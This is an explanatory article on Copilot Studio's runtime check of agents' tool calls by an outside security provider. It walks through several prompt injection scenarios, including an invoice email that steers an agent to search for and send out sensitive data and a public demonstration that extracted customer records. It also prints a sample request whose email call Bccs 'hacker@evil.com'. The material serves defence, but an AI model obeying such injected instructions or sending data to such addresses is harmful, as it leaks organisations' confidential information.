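# External threat detection in Microsoft Copilot Studio: approving or blocking an agent's tool calls at runtime

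## What is external threat detection in Copilot Studio, and why was it added?

External threat detection is a security feature of Microsoft Copilot Studio, a service organisations use to build AI agents without much programming. An agent is a program in which a language model answers requests and uses tools, for instance to search files, update a customer record or send an email. Once an administrator has switched the feature on, the agent sends the details of each planned tool use to an outside security service, the provider, which returns "allow" or "block". If the action is allowed, the agent carries on and the user notices nothing, but if it is blocked, the agent stops and tells the user that it has blocked the message. Microsoft calls this "bring your own protection" because the provider can be Microsoft Defender, another company's product or a service that the organisation wrote itself.

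Such a check is needed because instructions in a message or document can lead an agent to use its tools for an attacker's purposes. An organisation's ordinary access controls may not detect this misuse.

### How an agent works

People reach Copilot Studio agents through Microsoft 365 Copilot, Teams, SharePoint and other channels, according to *Copilot Studio*, an analyst's roadmap of the product (Sanfilippo, 2026). An agent draws on topics, tools and knowledge sources, which Microsoft's Defender researchers describe in a post on attacks against agents. Topics are conversation flows prepared by the agent's maker. Particular phrases from the user start a topic, which then proceeds step by step through questions, conditions and actions. Tools are capabilities the agent can call, such as a connector that writes to a customer database. Knowledge sources are the documents, websites and business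 systems the agent uses for its answers.

The orchestrator, which Microsoft's interface also calls the planner, decides how these components work together. It uses a language model to interpret a request, plan one or more steps and choose tools for them. Each use of a tool with specific input values, such as sending one email to one address, is a tool call. Microsoft calls this generative orchestration when the orchestrator makes these choices at runtime. Classic agents instead follow conversation flows that their makers wrote beforehand, and Microsoft doesn't apply external threat detection to them. The documentation gives no reason, but a plausible one is that the maker of a classic agent has already fixed the order of actions, so hostile text can change less of what the agent does.

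An event trigger, such as the arrival of an email, can start an agent without a person typing anything. Microsoft's researchers use the example of a finance agent that processes every message sent to a company's invoice mailbox. One tool enters the payment details in the customer database, another sends a confirmation to the sender, and the agent uses a policy file to answer questions about refunds and payment terms. The maker instructed the agent to handle only invoices and basic finance questions, but the orchestrator makes a new plan for each email, and the email's content influences that plan. Anyone who knows the address can therefore send text to the orchestrator without any employee having to read it first.

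### Direct and indirect prompt injection

In a prompt injection attack, someone feeds an agent text that overrides its intended behaviour. This works because the orchestrator's instructions and the material it processes are both in natural language, so the form of a sentence doesn't reliably show whether it is an instruction from the agent's maker or a line in an invoice.

In direct prompt injection, the person talking to the agent writes the hostile instructions. Microsoft calls this a user prompt injection attack (UPIA). In December 2025, the security vendor Tenable demonstrated one on a travel-booking agent, using a chat message to make the agent run its record-updating action and change a price from $1,000 to $0.

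Indirect prompt injection hides instructions in content that the agent reads, such as an email or a document. Microsoft abbreviates it as XPIA, for cross-prompt or cross-domain injection attack. In the invoice example, an outsider sends what looks like a bill, with added instructions to search the knowledge source for unrelated sensitive information and send it back. The orchestrator may treat these instructions as a legitimate part of the request and add a search and an email to its plan. The attacker doesn't need an account at the company or any direct interaction with the agent.

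Neither of the two added steps exceeds the agent's permissions. The maker gave the agent access to the knowledge source so that it could answer questions, and an email tool so that it could confirm invoices. Access control determines whether a given identity may perform a given operation, so it allows both steps. The purpose of the operations has changed, but a permission list does not record purpose. Microsoft's researchers compare an agent's capabilities to the ability to run code inside a sandbox bounded by everything the agent can do. Anyone who steers the agent's plan can therefore use any of those capabilities.

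The damage can be worse where the agent has wider access than the attacker. In another of the researchers' scenarios, an employee plants instructions in a SharePoint document he is allowed to edit. When the agent processes the document, it opens a file of transactions that the employee cannot read, then tries to email the contents to an outside address. Both scenarios are constructed, though the researchers describe them as inspired by observed and emerging techniques. Tighter permissions would limit what an attacker can reach, but an agent with no access to anything valuable would be of little use. Help Net Security's *Microsoft wants to limit AI agents' permissions* (2026), on a newer set of Microsoft controls, acknowledges that an agent whose access is entirely appropriate can still come across a malicious instruction in an external document.

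### The Black Hat demonstration

The best-known example of an attack on Copilot Studio itself comes from Zenity, which sells security products for AI agents. At the Black Hat USA conference in August 2025, its co-founder Michael Bargury and researcher Tamir Ishay Sharbat presented AgentFlayer (Zenity Labs, 2025), a collection of attacks on ChatGPT, Copilot Studio, Salesforce Einstein, Cursor and other products. The attacks were "0click", meaning they required no action from a legitimate user.

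On its YouTube channel, Microsoft had shown a customer-service agent by the consulting firm McKinsey as an example of what Copilot Studio could do. *A Customer Service AI Agent Spits Out Complete Salesforce Records* (Mitchell, 2025) describes the agent as dealing with customers by itself and searching internal knowledge bases and data systems for its replies. The researchers built a replica and attacked that, according to Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer*. After a preliminary discovery stage, they got the replica to output complete customer records from Salesforce, a widely used customer database. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, reposted an account of the attack, *A Copilot Studio Story 2* (Sharbat, 2025), on 16 July, before the conference.

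Zenity attributes the result to a combination of settings: untrusted people could reach the agent, it accepted their messages without authentication, and it held privileged permissions. Zenity calls such an agent misconfigured, which places part of the fault with whoever builds it. Yet Mitchell reports that Microsoft responded with a patch, so the company evidently found something of its own to correct. About a month after the conference, Cohen (2025) wrote for Microsoft Defender in *Protect Copilot Studio AI Agents in Real Time with Microsoft Defender* that the risks of prompt injection "aren't due to flaws in Copilot Studio or any single platform".

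Both companies have something to sell. Zenity follows its summary of the attack with a pitch for its own product, which plugs into Copilot Studio and checks agents' actions. The target was a copy, so the demonstration is evidence about a design that Microsoft had held up as exemplary, not about a leak of real customers' data. Still, it makes the invoice scenario more than hypothetical, since an agent of the same general kind gave records to a stranger.

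Microsoft announced the feature a month after the Black Hat demonstration, which illustrates the problem well but probably did not prompt it. The interface through which agents contact a provider is labeled version 2025-05-01 in Microsoft's developer documentation, which suggests that its design was under way before Zenity's account appeared in July.

### The built-in filters, and why Microsoft added another check

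Copilot Studio already had defences against both kinds of injection, and they remain active by default without an outside service. In its announcement of the new feature, Microsoft said these built-in filters block suspicious prompts in real time to reduce the risk of data loss or unauthorised actions. *What's new in Copilot Studio* (2025), Microsoft's February roundup, had already reported better detection of indirect injection. Microsoft later declared the protection against indirect injection generally available and added a display that shows makers each agent's protection status. Neither the announcement nor the documentation of the new feature gives figures for how many attacks the filters catch or miss.

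In its announcement, Microsoft writes that the built-in protections "may not be enough" for organisations with "advanced security needs", and that agents are taking on more sensitive work and starting more often without a user. Copilot Studio also lets people without technical training build and deploy agents, often with no central security review, as Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime* acknowledges. A security team in that position cannot count on having inspected an agent before it goes live, but it can still inspect what the agent does.

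Timing is another reason to check tool calls. Hostile instructions can take endless forms, and a filter that examines text has to recognise them among legitimate requests. A tool call is more concrete because it specifies the file, the recipient and the contents. In Cohen's example, a hidden prompt induces a human-resources chatbot to send out confidential salary information. The prompt may have looked harmless, but a plan to send salaries to someone who shouldn't receive them is easier to recognise as a problem, and the check happens before the email is sent. The provider has one second to decide, according to Visual Studio Magazine (2025).

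The built-in filters and the external check may overlap, because Microsoft describes its built-in protection as blocking malicious "inputs or actions", not just malicious text. A clearer difference is who sets the rules. Microsoft designs the filters to catch attacks, whereas an organisation that chooses its own provider can also have it block actions that are not attacks. Microsoft gives the example of an email that would share too much information, whatever the agent's reason for writing it. Directions on Microsoft (2025), an independent analyst firm, described similar benefits in November 2025: with the new check, Defender inspects every tool call, and the organisation gets a log of those calls and may be able to add other vendors' detection or its own.

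A year later, in October 2026, Microsoft vice-president Nadim Abdo made a more general case for outside control. According to TechRadar's *Microsoft admits 'frontier models can't be trusted'*, he wrote that "we should not ask a model to be its own security authority", and that controls must sit where the model cannot bypass them. Abdo was introducing different products, but external threat detection follows the same principle, with a separate system approving or blocking the tool calls that the orchestrator proposes.

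### Release history and current status

Microsoft announced the public preview on 8 September 2025 and promised availability to all customers by 10 September. The route from preview to general availability is much harder to follow. General availability is the stage at which Microsoft considers a feature finished and ready for production use.

Microsoft's *Strengthen security of Copilot Studio agents with additional threat protection* (2025), a notice to administrators dated 27 October and revised on 3 November, belongs to the first attempt. The revised notice gave 10 December 2025 as the general availability date, but it referred readers to setup instructions that still had "(preview)" in their title. In February 2026, Microsoft's documentation still had the preview label and the standard warning that preview features are not meant for production use.

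Microsoft's release plan, as it stood on 23 June 2026, listed the preview as released on 4 September 2025 and gave a new date for general availability, "Jun 2026". The plan shows a full date for features that Microsoft has released and only a month for those still to come, so the feature was not yet generally available on 23 June. *Runtime Protection and External Threat Detection*, a governance guide for financial firms last checked in May 2026, also treated the feature as a preview and advised against using it yet for agents that handle customer data. On 28 June, Sanfilippo still listed Defender's monitoring of agents as "in preview".

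The setup page for Defender had no preview notice in May, and Microsoft's developer page had none in June. This is only weak evidence that the feature had been released, because Microsoft's own plan listed the release as pending. The June version of Microsoft's *What's new in Copilot Studio* has no entry for the feature reaching general availability, but this is inconclusive because the page lists only notable changes and has nothing under its December 2025 heading.

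Microsoft (2026) told administrators that on 2 July 2026 it began publishing its plans for Copilot Studio on the Microsoft 365 Roadmap and stopped maintaining the old release planner for them. Readers therefore cannot tell from the June entry whether Microsoft met its date.

Licensing changed in the same week, at least for customers who use Defender as their provider. From 1 July, Microsoft requires a licence for Agent 365, its product for managing and securing agents, and planned to disable Defender's real-time protection of Copilot Studio agents for organisations without one. In July Microsoft described runtime protection for these agents as part of Agent 365, and Petri's *Microsoft Defender Adds Runtime Protection for AI Agents in Agent 365* presented it the same way in September. Defender's service is therefore now part of Agent 365, but it is unclear whether the underlying connection,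 which other vendors' and home-built services also use, has left preview. Microsoft's later pages do not support the December 2025 date, and general availability may have come in June 2026, later or not at all. Organisations planning to use the feature in production should first confirm its status with Microsoft.

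## How does Copilot Studio ask for a decision before a tool is used?

Whenever the orchestrator chooses to use a tool, Copilot Studio asks for a decision by automatically sending a web request to an address that the provider has supplied. Developers call an address used this way a webhook. The request describes the planned tool call and the conversation that led to it.

### One tool call from plan to outcome

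Suppose an employee asks an agent to email a customer. The orchestrator finds the customer's address with a lookup tool, then selects a tool that sends email and fills in its inputs, such as the recipient. Before running the email tool, Copilot Studio contacts the provider and waits for an answer. If the answer is "allow", the tool runs, but if it is "block", the email isn't sent.

Microsoft's announcement and its developer documentation differ slightly on the timing of the check. According to the announcement, Copilot Studio sends the agent's plan to the provider before the agent begins to carry it out. According to the documentation, the agent contacts the provider every time it intends to use a tool. The documentation is probably the better guide, because the request has a field for the results of earlier tools, and those results cannot exist until part of the plan has run. Repeated checks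 also make sense as a defence against indirect prompt injection, because the agent may open a document containing hostile text halfway through its work, when an approval given at the start would be out of date.

The check may cover more than tools. Microsoft (2026) includes topics and knowledge searches among the actions that Copilot Studio submits to Defender. In the invoice example, the request would contain the agent's search terms, the outputs of earlier steps and context from the email that started the process. Defender could then stop the attack by blocking the search, before the agent had found any information to steal. The developer documentation mentions only tools, so an organisation that wants its own provider to check knowledge searches should confirm that the provider receives those requests.

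### The two endpoints

A provider has to offer two endpoints, which are web addresses that each accept one kind of request. The first, `validate`, is for setting up and testing the connection. Copilot Studio sends it a request with an empty body, and a working service returns an `isSuccessful` field and a short status message. The main endpoint, `analyze-tool-execution`, receives the details of each planned tool call and returns the decision.

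Requests to both endpoints include a version label and a token that identifies the caller. Microsoft asks developers not to reject a request because of an unfamiliar version or an unexpected field, since it may add fields later.

A provider can implement the interface with very little code. *Microsoft External Threat Detection* (2025), a developer's blog post about building a provider, gives a few lines for each endpoint as a simple starting point. `validate` always reports success, and `analyze-tool-execution` records each request and allows every action. The developer reports that agent events began to reach the service once the set-up was complete. A working connection therefore shows only that a service answers in the right format, not that it can recognise an attack.

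### What the request contains

Every request to `analyze-tool-execution` has four parts. Some of the fields within them are optional, as Microsoft's field list shows:

| Part | Always included | Optional |
|---|---|---|
| Planner context | The user's message | The orchestrator's reason for choosing the tool, recent chat messages, outputs of earlier tools |
| Tool definition | The tool's ID, type, name and description | The inputs the tool accepts and the outputs it returns |
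| Input values | The values for this particular call | None listed |
| Conversation metadata | IDs for the agent, its tenant, its environment and the conversation; whether the agent is a published version | The agent's version, the user, the trigger, the plan and step, any parent agent |

A tenant is an organisation's account in Microsoft's cloud, and an environment is an administrative container within it for agents and data.

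The planner context includes a `thought` field containing the orchestrator's reason for choosing the tool, which can help a provider interpret an unusual request. But this reason comes from the same language model that an attacker may have manipulated, so a sensible-sounding one is weak evidence that the call is safe.

The tool definition describes the tool in general, so a provider needs the input values to see what the agent is about to do with it. For example, an email tool's definition may include a Bcc field, but only the input values show who is in it. A provider can use the metadata to apply different rules to different agents, or to treat a live agent more strictly than one still in testing. User details are optional, presumably because an event can start an agent without anyone in the conversation.

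Optional fields may be missing from a request, so a service that needs the chat history to reach a decision must still return a response without it. Developers also need to be careful with the field name for earlier tool results, which is `previousToolOutputs` in Microsoft's sample request but `previousToolsOutputs` in its field list. Microsoft does not let organisations customise which data Copilot Studio shares, so those that object to sending chat history, for example, have to leave the feature off.

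### Microsoft's example: an unknown address in the Bcc field

Microsoft's developer documentation illustrates the exchange with a user who asks an agent to send an email to a customer. The agent asks which customer, and the user names John Doe. The agent then looks up John Doe's address and prepares the email. Shortened, and with the planned call moved to the top, the resulting request looks like this:

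```json
{
  "toolDefinition": { "name": "Send email" },
  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
  },
  "plannerContext": {
    "thought": "User wants to notify customer",
    "userMessage": "Send an email to the customer",
    "previousToolOutputs": [
      {
        "toolName": "Get customer email by name",
        "outputs": { "value": "customer@foobar.com" }
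      }
    ],
    "chatHistory": ["..."]
  },
  "conversationMetadata": {
    "agent": { "isPublished": true },
    "conversationId": "conv-id"
  }
}
```

The main recipient is easy to account for. The user asked for an email to John Doe, and the lookup returned the address that now stands in the `to` field. Nothing in the request explains the Bcc address. The user didn't mention a second recipient, no earlier tool returned one, and the orchestrator's stated reason covers only the customer. Microsoft doesn't explain how the address got there, and the provider doesn't need to know in order to object to it. The provider's answer, again shortened, is a block:

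```json
{
  "blockAction": true,
  "reasonCode": 112,
  "reason": "... noncompliant email address in the BCC field."
}
```

`blockAction` is the only required field. A provider may add a numeric code, a written explanation and a `diagnostics` field with technical details. In this example, `diagnostics` identifies the Bcc field and the address in it. Each provider defines its own codes, so 112 can mean different things in different products. If the provider cannot process a request, for instance because the tool definition is missing, it returns an error message instead of a decision.

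The provider can only allow or block a call. It cannot remove the Bcc address and let the rest of the email go, and the format has no field for asking a person to confirm the call. This may surprise customers whose security product normally edits data. *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, CrowdStrike's guide to connecting its security service, warns that a rule designed to transform data will only report what it finds and will allow the call. Customers who want to stop such calls have to choose a blocking rule.

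### What happens after a block

According to Microsoft's developer documentation, an agent skips a tool when the call is blocked, but according to the setup documentation, the agent immediately stops processing and notifies the user that it has blocked their message. An agent that only skipped the tool might continue with its plan or look for another way to reach the same goal. Microsoft's announcement also describes the agent as stopping, so a full stop is the better-supported reading. In either case, the block applies only to a tool that has not yet run, so if the agent updated a customer record two steps earlier, the update remains.

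The notice may puzzle a user who has done nothing wrong. For example, someone who asks for a summary of a document containing hidden instructions will see that the agent blocked their message, even though the problem is in the document. Microsoft does not promise in its documentation that the user will see the provider's reason.

Administrators get more information, because a blocked call appears in the agent's Activity History with an error message attributing the failure to threat detection. This record is particularly useful for agents that start when an email arrives, since there may be nobody in a chat to notify. If Defender is the provider, the security team also receives an alert in the Defender portal, but only if Defender has been separately linked to Microsoft 365. Microsoft notes that without this link, Defender still blocks suspicious calls but the alerts don't appear in the portal.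 The security team could then miss a series of blocked attacks.

### When the answer is late or missing

*Microsoft External Threat Detection* says of the provider's one-second limit, "good luck with that". Copilot Studio waits for the provider before every tool call, so a plan with five calls in a row could take almost five seconds longer, even if the provider always answers in time.

Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about what happens when the time runs out. In the setup form, as Microsoft documented it in February 2026, the administrator chooses an error behaviour for when the provider responds too late or returns an error. The default is "Allow the agent to respond" (failing open), and the alternative is "Block the query" (failing closed). But according to a note further down the same page, the agent uses the tool if it receives no decision within one second. The note makes no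 exception for administrators who chose to block.

Microsoft's newer text leaves it unclear whether the error setting applies to late answers. In June 2026 the developer documentation still treated a late answer as "allow", without mentioning the setting. According to CrowdStrike, Copilot Studio instead applies the behaviour the administrator has selected if no answer arrives within one second. *Control 1.8 Troubleshooting*, a community guide for financial firms, describes late answers the same way and adds that the setting also covers server errors and the provider's rejection of the agent's credentials.

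Most likely, the setting works and Microsoft's flat statements describe the default. Those statements may also be older than the option to block. Zenity's guide to the same form has no step for error behaviour, which would fit with the option being added later, but the guide may just omit the step. Neither CrowdStrike nor the community guide describes testing a late answer with the block option on. An organisation that needs to fail closed should therefore test this by selecting "Block the query" in a trial environment and connecting it to a service that waits two seconds before answering. If the tool runs anyway, the setting does not cover late answers.

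### How the provider knows who is asking

A provider needs to tell whether a request comes from a customer's agent or from a stranger who has found the provider's web address. Copilot Studio uses Microsoft Entra, Microsoft's identity service, for this. The customer registers an application in Entra, and the agents contact the provider under that application's identity.

Copilot Studio proves its identity with a federated identity credential, an entry in the application's registration that specifies which outside identity Entra should trust to act as the application. Applications often use a stored secret for this, similar to a password, which someone has to protect and renew. The setup documentation requires two main details in the entry, the issuer and the subject. The issuer is Microsoft's login service for the customer's tenant. The subject is a long string that includes the customer's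 tenant ID and the provider's address in encoded form.

When Copilot Studio needs a token, it presents an identity statement to Entra, which compares the issuer and subject with the entry. If they match, Entra issues the token and Copilot Studio attaches it to the request. The configuration contains no secret for an attacker to steal. The match must be exact, so Microsoft warns against extra spaces in the subject, and a customer whose provider moves to a new address must also update the credential.

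The token protects the provider only if the provider checks it. Microsoft leaves this to the developer, who must verify incoming tokens and decide which applications to accept, for example with a list of approved application IDs. Zenity asks customers to enter their application and tenant IDs in its portal, then adds the application to its list. For Defender, an administrator enters the application ID in the Defender portal, and it must match the one in Power Platform. The sample code in *Microsoft External Threat Detection* reads the application and tenant IDs from the token but doesn't check that the token is genuine. This is adequate for a demonstration, but a real service built that way would accept requests from anyone who knew its address.

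### Setting up the connection

Setting up the feature usually involves more than one team, because the Entra application and the Copilot Studio connection require different permissions. Administrators can create the application and its credential by hand or with a Microsoft script, which has a trial mode that checks the details without creating anything. Building a custom provider takes more work. *Microsoft External Threat Detection* describes having to prove ownership of the service's web domain to Microsoft, and calls the whole procedure "super complex".

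The remaining steps take place in the Power Platform admin center and require the Power Platform Administrator role. The administrator opens the threat detection page, selects an environment and allows Copilot Studio to share data with a provider. The administrator then enters the application ID and the provider's address, and chooses the error behaviour. When the administrator saves these settings, Copilot Studio tests the connection and rejects it if the Entra application is misconfigured or the provider has not authorised the application.

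Administrators can apply the settings to a single environment, several environments or an environment group. Different environments can use different providers, so a company could try out a home-built service in a test environment while Defender checks its live agents. Makers don't have to change their agents, and they can't disconnect the provider unless they have the administrator role. The drawback is that agents in an environment with no connected provider have only the built-in filters.

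### Audit logs

In its announcement, Microsoft promised detailed audit logs of every interaction between Copilot Studio and the provider, so that administrators could trace attempted attacks, find vulnerable agents and judge how well the provider performs. According to Directions on Microsoft, the log of agents' outbound tool calls is kept in Purview, Microsoft's compliance and auditing service.

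As of May 2026, Microsoft's list of Copilot Studio events in Purview has no separate event for a provider's decision. It lists changes to agents, such as creating or publishing one, and a general event for conversations with users, called `CopilotInteraction`. That event may include the decision, but Microsoft's description mentions only information such as the time, the user and the transcript ID. Purview's audit log does not contain the text of the conversation, which Copilot Studio stores separately.

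According to *Control 1.8 Troubleshooting*, searching the log for the record type "CopilotStudio" returns nothing, without any warning, because the correct type is `CopilotInteraction`. A simple search also stops at 5,000 rows, so an investigator looking at a busy agent could miss the relevant entry.

Datadog Security Labs found that Copilot Studio failed to log some administrative actions that Microsoft's documentation listed. After Datadog reported four such events, it still could not observe consistent logging for two of them. The finding concerns changes to agents, not the exchange with a provider, but it is a good reason to test the logs before relying on them in an investigation.

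The provider's records can fill some of the gaps. CrowdStrike, for example, logs the latest user message, the conversation history and the tool's inputs, although customers can limit the logs to metadata. These records are more useful than a transcript ID for working out why the provider blocked a call. But they cannot include requests that never reached the provider, so an investigator looking for unchecked tool calls also needs a record from Copilot Studio.

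## Who makes the decision, and what information do they use?

The provider decides whether a tool call goes ahead, and it can use any method. Microsoft fixes the format of the request and the answer. In its developer documentation, it describes the decision only as an evaluation "based on the defined criteria", and the provider has to define those criteria. Two providers can therefore give opposite answers to the same request, and Copilot Studio will act on whichever answer it receives.

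The choice of provider also determines who receives the agent's chat messages and the results of its earlier tool calls. Microsoft warns that a provider's data-handling policies may differ from Microsoft's and that the provider may store the data in another region. It leaves customers to check the provider's terms.

Three other security vendors have publicly described their integrations. Zenity and CrowdStrike, whose product is called AIDR, have setup guides. Palo Alto Networks announced support in its Prisma AIRS product in *Prisma AIRS Integrates with Microsoft Copilot Studio for AI Security* (Agarwal and Leung, 2025).

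| Provider | Information used for the decision | What it is meant to detect |
|---|---|---|
| Defender, according to Microsoft | The planned action and its inputs, outputs of earlier steps, user details and other metadata | Prompt injection, data theft, probing of an agent's capabilities |
| Zenity | The planned call, the orchestrator's reason for it, chat messages, earlier tool outputs, metadata | Direct and indirect prompt injection, data theft, careless handling of passwords and other secrets |
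| Prisma AIRS, according to Agarwal and Leung | The planned call, chat messages, metadata | Prompt injection, data leaks, malicious code, impersonation, misuse of tools |
| CrowdStrike AIDR | The tool's name and input values only | Malicious activity, sensitive data and forbidden topics, depending on the customer's policy |
| Home-built service | Any part of the request that the developer chooses | Whatever the developer writes rules for |

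### Microsoft Defender

Microsoft has described Defender's method in two ways. At the launch, Cohen gave a known prompt injection pattern as an example of what makes Defender block a call, which suggests that it compares calls with earlier attacks. In January 2026, Microsoft's Defender researchers wrote that Defender evaluates the intent and destination of every action, which would take more interpretation. Defender may well do both, but Microsoft doesn't explain how it combines them, whether it uses a language model, or how strong the evidence must be for it to block a call. Microsoft's setup instructions cover connecting Defender but include no step for choosing what it should block.

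The researchers illustrate the check with three attacks, which Defender stops at different points. In the invoice scenario, Defender blocks the search for sensitive information. This is the best point to stop the attack, but it is also difficult because the agent hasn't yet tried to send anything. Defender has to determine from the search terms and the email that the search is unrelated to handling an invoice.

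In the SharePoint scenario, Defender prevents the leak by blocking the email to the outside address, but only after the agent has read the confidential file. The researchers don't specify what evidence Defender used, but they credit the detection to Microsoft Threat Intelligence, which may mean that Microsoft already knew the attacker's domain. If so, a newly registered domain would be harder to detect.

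The third scenario involves a support chatbot on a company's public website that visitors can use without signing in. Its knowledge base includes customer information and internal contact details. An attacker asks it a series of carefully written questions to find out what tools and data it has, intending to extract the data later. Defender detects the probing and blocks the resulting tool calls. Since Copilot Studio contacts a provider only before an action, Defender presumably recognises the probing from the chat history it receives before one of these tool calls. The attacker may still learn something from replies the chatbot gives without using a tool.

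Defender succeeds in all three constructed scenarios, but the researchers don't report how many attacks they tried, what share Defender caught or how many legitimate calls it blocked. The scenarios therefore illustrate the intended behaviour but not how reliable it is.

After a block, Defender raises an informational alert and looks for related activity in the organisation's email, devices, user accounts and cloud services. It groups the results into a single incident for the security team. According to Cohen, most single alerts need no immediate response because Defender has already stopped the action. Defender also flags sustained activity by the same attacker or with the same technique. In the invoice case, an analyst might discover that the same sender had written to several other mailboxes. Cohen describes this search as starting after the block, so it helps with the investigation, but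 there is no evidence that it informs the decision to block.

Microsoft says Defender also keeps an inventory of Copilot Studio agents and continuously monitors their audit logs. The monitoring can produce an alert after an agent has acted, but only the real-time check can stop a tool call before it runs.

### Zenity, Palo Alto Networks and CrowdStrike

Zenity receives all the main kinds of data that Copilot Studio shares, but its setup guide does not explain how the product uses them to reach a decision. In the press release launching the integration, Zenity (2025) said that the product analysed "intent and behavior signals". In a press release two months later, Zenity emphasised "hard boundaries" and "deterministic" controls, meaning fixed rules that always give the same answer to the same input, such as a ban on emailing customer records outside the company. Assessments of intent, by contrast,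 are usually probabilistic. The product may use both methods, but a buyer needs to know which threats each one covers, because a fixed rule can be checked with a few test cases, while measuring how well a product judges intent takes many realistic attacks and harmless requests.

Agarwal and Leung give an example close to Microsoft's own, in which Prisma AIRS blocks an email to the wrong recipient. They don't explain how the product identifies a wrong recipient. Their list of the data it receives omits the outputs of earlier tools, which could show, for example, that a lookup had returned a particular customer's address. The list may be incomplete, since Copilot Studio can send those outputs to any provider. Agarwal and Leung also promise that the checks won't slow down a business, but they give no response times.

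CrowdStrike is the most open about a limitation. AIDR receives the user's message, the chat history and the outputs of earlier tools, but CrowdStrike says it analyses only the tool's name and input values. The company explains that the user has already submitted the prompt to the agent's language model by the time Copilot Studio contacts AIDR. AIDR can't keep the prompt from the model at that point, but it could still use the prompt to judge whether the tool call is what the user wanted. AIDR also doesn't analyse hostile text in a document unless the orchestrator copies some of it into the inputs of a later call.

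The policy a customer assigns to AIDR determines what it blocks. Without a policy, it records the agents' activity and applies no detection rules. CrowdStrike advises customers to start by monitoring and then add blocking rules for the risks they find. Two companies with the same product can therefore have very different levels of protection, and a company that only monitors does not block any tool calls.

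### Home-built services

An organisation that builds its own provider can enforce rules specific to its business. For example, it could limit the domains each agent may email, or allow only one agent to issue refunds. It can also keep the conversations on systems it controls instead of passing them to an outside security company.

Writing the rules is the difficult part. Microsoft documents the interface and gives example responses, but not the logic that would produce them. The developer's demonstration in *Microsoft External Threat Detection* doesn't supply that logic either, since it logs each request and then allows it. A service that only logs requests is still a reasonable first version. A team can run it for a few weeks, learn which recipients and search terms are normal for each agent, and then write rules that don't interrupt ordinary work.

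### Three ways to judge the Bcc email

Microsoft's example shows how much the choice of information matters. The email to John Doe has `hacker@evil.com` in the Bcc field, but the lookup tool had returned only the customer's address.

A service that, like AIDR, uses only the tool's name and inputs can block the email if `evil.com` is on a list of hostile domains, or if the company forbids Bcc recipients outside its own domain. But if the attacker used an ordinary-looking address at an unknown domain, instead of the suspicious one in Microsoft's example, the input values alone would not show which of the two recipients the user wanted.

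A service that also compares the inputs with what the user asked for has a better chance, because it can detect that neither the user nor the lookup supplied the second address, however harmless that address looks. But an unexplained recipient can be legitimate. For example, the agent's maker may have instructed it to copy all customer emails to a sales archive. The request sent to the service has no field for the maker's instructions, so the archive's address would look just as unexplained as the attacker's.

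A provider could fill this gap by keeping its own record of what each agent is for. Defender may be well placed to do this, because its agent inventory includes a column for each agent's instructions, according to sample queries published by the security blogger Rod Trent. Microsoft does not say whether the real-time check uses that column.

The third method is a fixed rule that every recipient must appear somewhere in the chat or in the output of an earlier tool. The service takes each address from the `to` and `bcc` fields and searches for it in the rest of the request. It finds the customer's address in the lookup result but doesn't find the attacker's, so it blocks the email. This simple text search should easily finish within the one-second limit, and it works even if nobody has seen the attacker's domain before. The rule would also block emails to the sales archive. It would sometimes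 block emails to an address that the user gave early in a long conversation, because Copilot Studio sends only recent messages and tool outputs.

The rule can't distinguish an attacker from a genuine sender when the attacker's address arrives in the email that started the agent, because the finance agent is supposed to send a confirmation to whoever submitted the invoice. Whether the rule finds the address depends on how Copilot Studio passes on the email, which is unclear from the developer documentation. The `trigger` field contains only an ID and a schema name, but Microsoft's Defender researchers say that the request includes context from the email. If the email's text appears among the chat messages, the rule finds the attacker's address and allows the reply. If the text is missing and no earlier tool has returned the address, the rule blocks the reply to the attacker along with every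 genuine confirmation.

The SharePoint attack can defeat the rule in a similar way. If the employee writes the outside address into the document, the address appears in the output of the tool that reads the document, so the rule accepts it.

Comparing the action with the user's request doesn't solve the invoice case either, because no employee has made a request. The only request is in the attacker's email, and the search for sensitive information matches it. To detect the problem, the service would need to compare the search with the agent's job, which is to process invoices. A service that uses only the inputs might do better here than in the Bcc example, because a rule against sending sensitive data can stop a reply that contains customer records or bank details, whoever the recipient is.

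These failures happen because the request does not record where each input value came from. A provider can search the chat and the tool outputs for an address, but finding it there doesn't prove that the orchestrator took it from that source or that the source was trustworthy.

A stricter rule could use the tool names attached to earlier outputs to accept an address from the customer lookup but reject one from the text of a document. This would stop the SharePoint attack but would also block some legitimate emails to people named in documents. It would not help the finance agent, whose normal work includes replying to strangers. For that agent, a provider has to judge what the agent is looking for or about to send.

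### The licence for Defender's check

Microsoft moved Defender's real-time check for Copilot Studio agents to Agent 365 on 1 July 2026. Before that, customers got it through Defender for Cloud Apps, an older security product. Two statements on Microsoft's page about the move, as it stood in June, are hard to reconcile. Microsoft listed real-time protection of Copilot Studio agents among the features it would disable for organisations without an Agent 365 licence. Further down, it said that the same protection through Defender for Cloud Apps "remains unchanged" for organisations that continue to use it, and that they didn't need to do anything.

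"Unchanged" most likely refers to the settings, not the licence. In the same passage, Microsoft tells customers of a different Agent 365 check that their blocking rules will stop working on 1 July unless they recreate them. Customers of the Copilot Studio check don't have to redo anything, but on this reading they still need the new licence.

Evidence from after the change supports this reading. In *AI Features Cut from Defender for Cloud to Enhance Agent 365*, written for the analyst firm Directions on Microsoft, Miller (2026) wrote on 6 July that customers must now license Agent 365 to get comparable features. He lists real-time protection for Copilot Studio agents among the affected features. A licensing guide, schneider.im's *Microsoft Agent 365*, gives the same date and says Defender's agent protection was free in preview. The main evidence against this reading is Microsoft's *Discover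 and protect your Copilot Studio AI Agents (Preview)*, which in June still listed a combination of older licences as sufficient. But that page concerns the inventory and detection features, and the June version predates the change.

Organisations should assume that Defender's check requires Agent 365. Those with an older licence should test whether Defender still blocks anything. Microsoft does not say what happens to an agent's tool calls if Defender stops serving an unlicensed customer while the connection stays in place. If Copilot Studio treats that refusal of service as an error, its default setting would let the calls proceed.

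Microsoft sells Agent 365 per user. According to Licensing School's *Agent 365 FAQs* (2026), one licence covers all the agents a person uses, manages or sponsors, and the agents need no licence. A single agent with 5,000 users could therefore require far more licences than fifty agents with ten users between them. Since 1 June, buyers have also needed a qualifying Microsoft 365 plan for these users, such as E5 or Business Premium. Microsoft offers a 30-day trial for 25 users, which is enough to test the connection.

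The transition page covers only Microsoft's own security features. It contains no requirement to buy Agent 365 to use a provider from another vendor or one built in-house, although the vendors charge for their products. CrowdStrike, for example, requires a subscription to AIDR for Agents.

### The separate check in Agent 365

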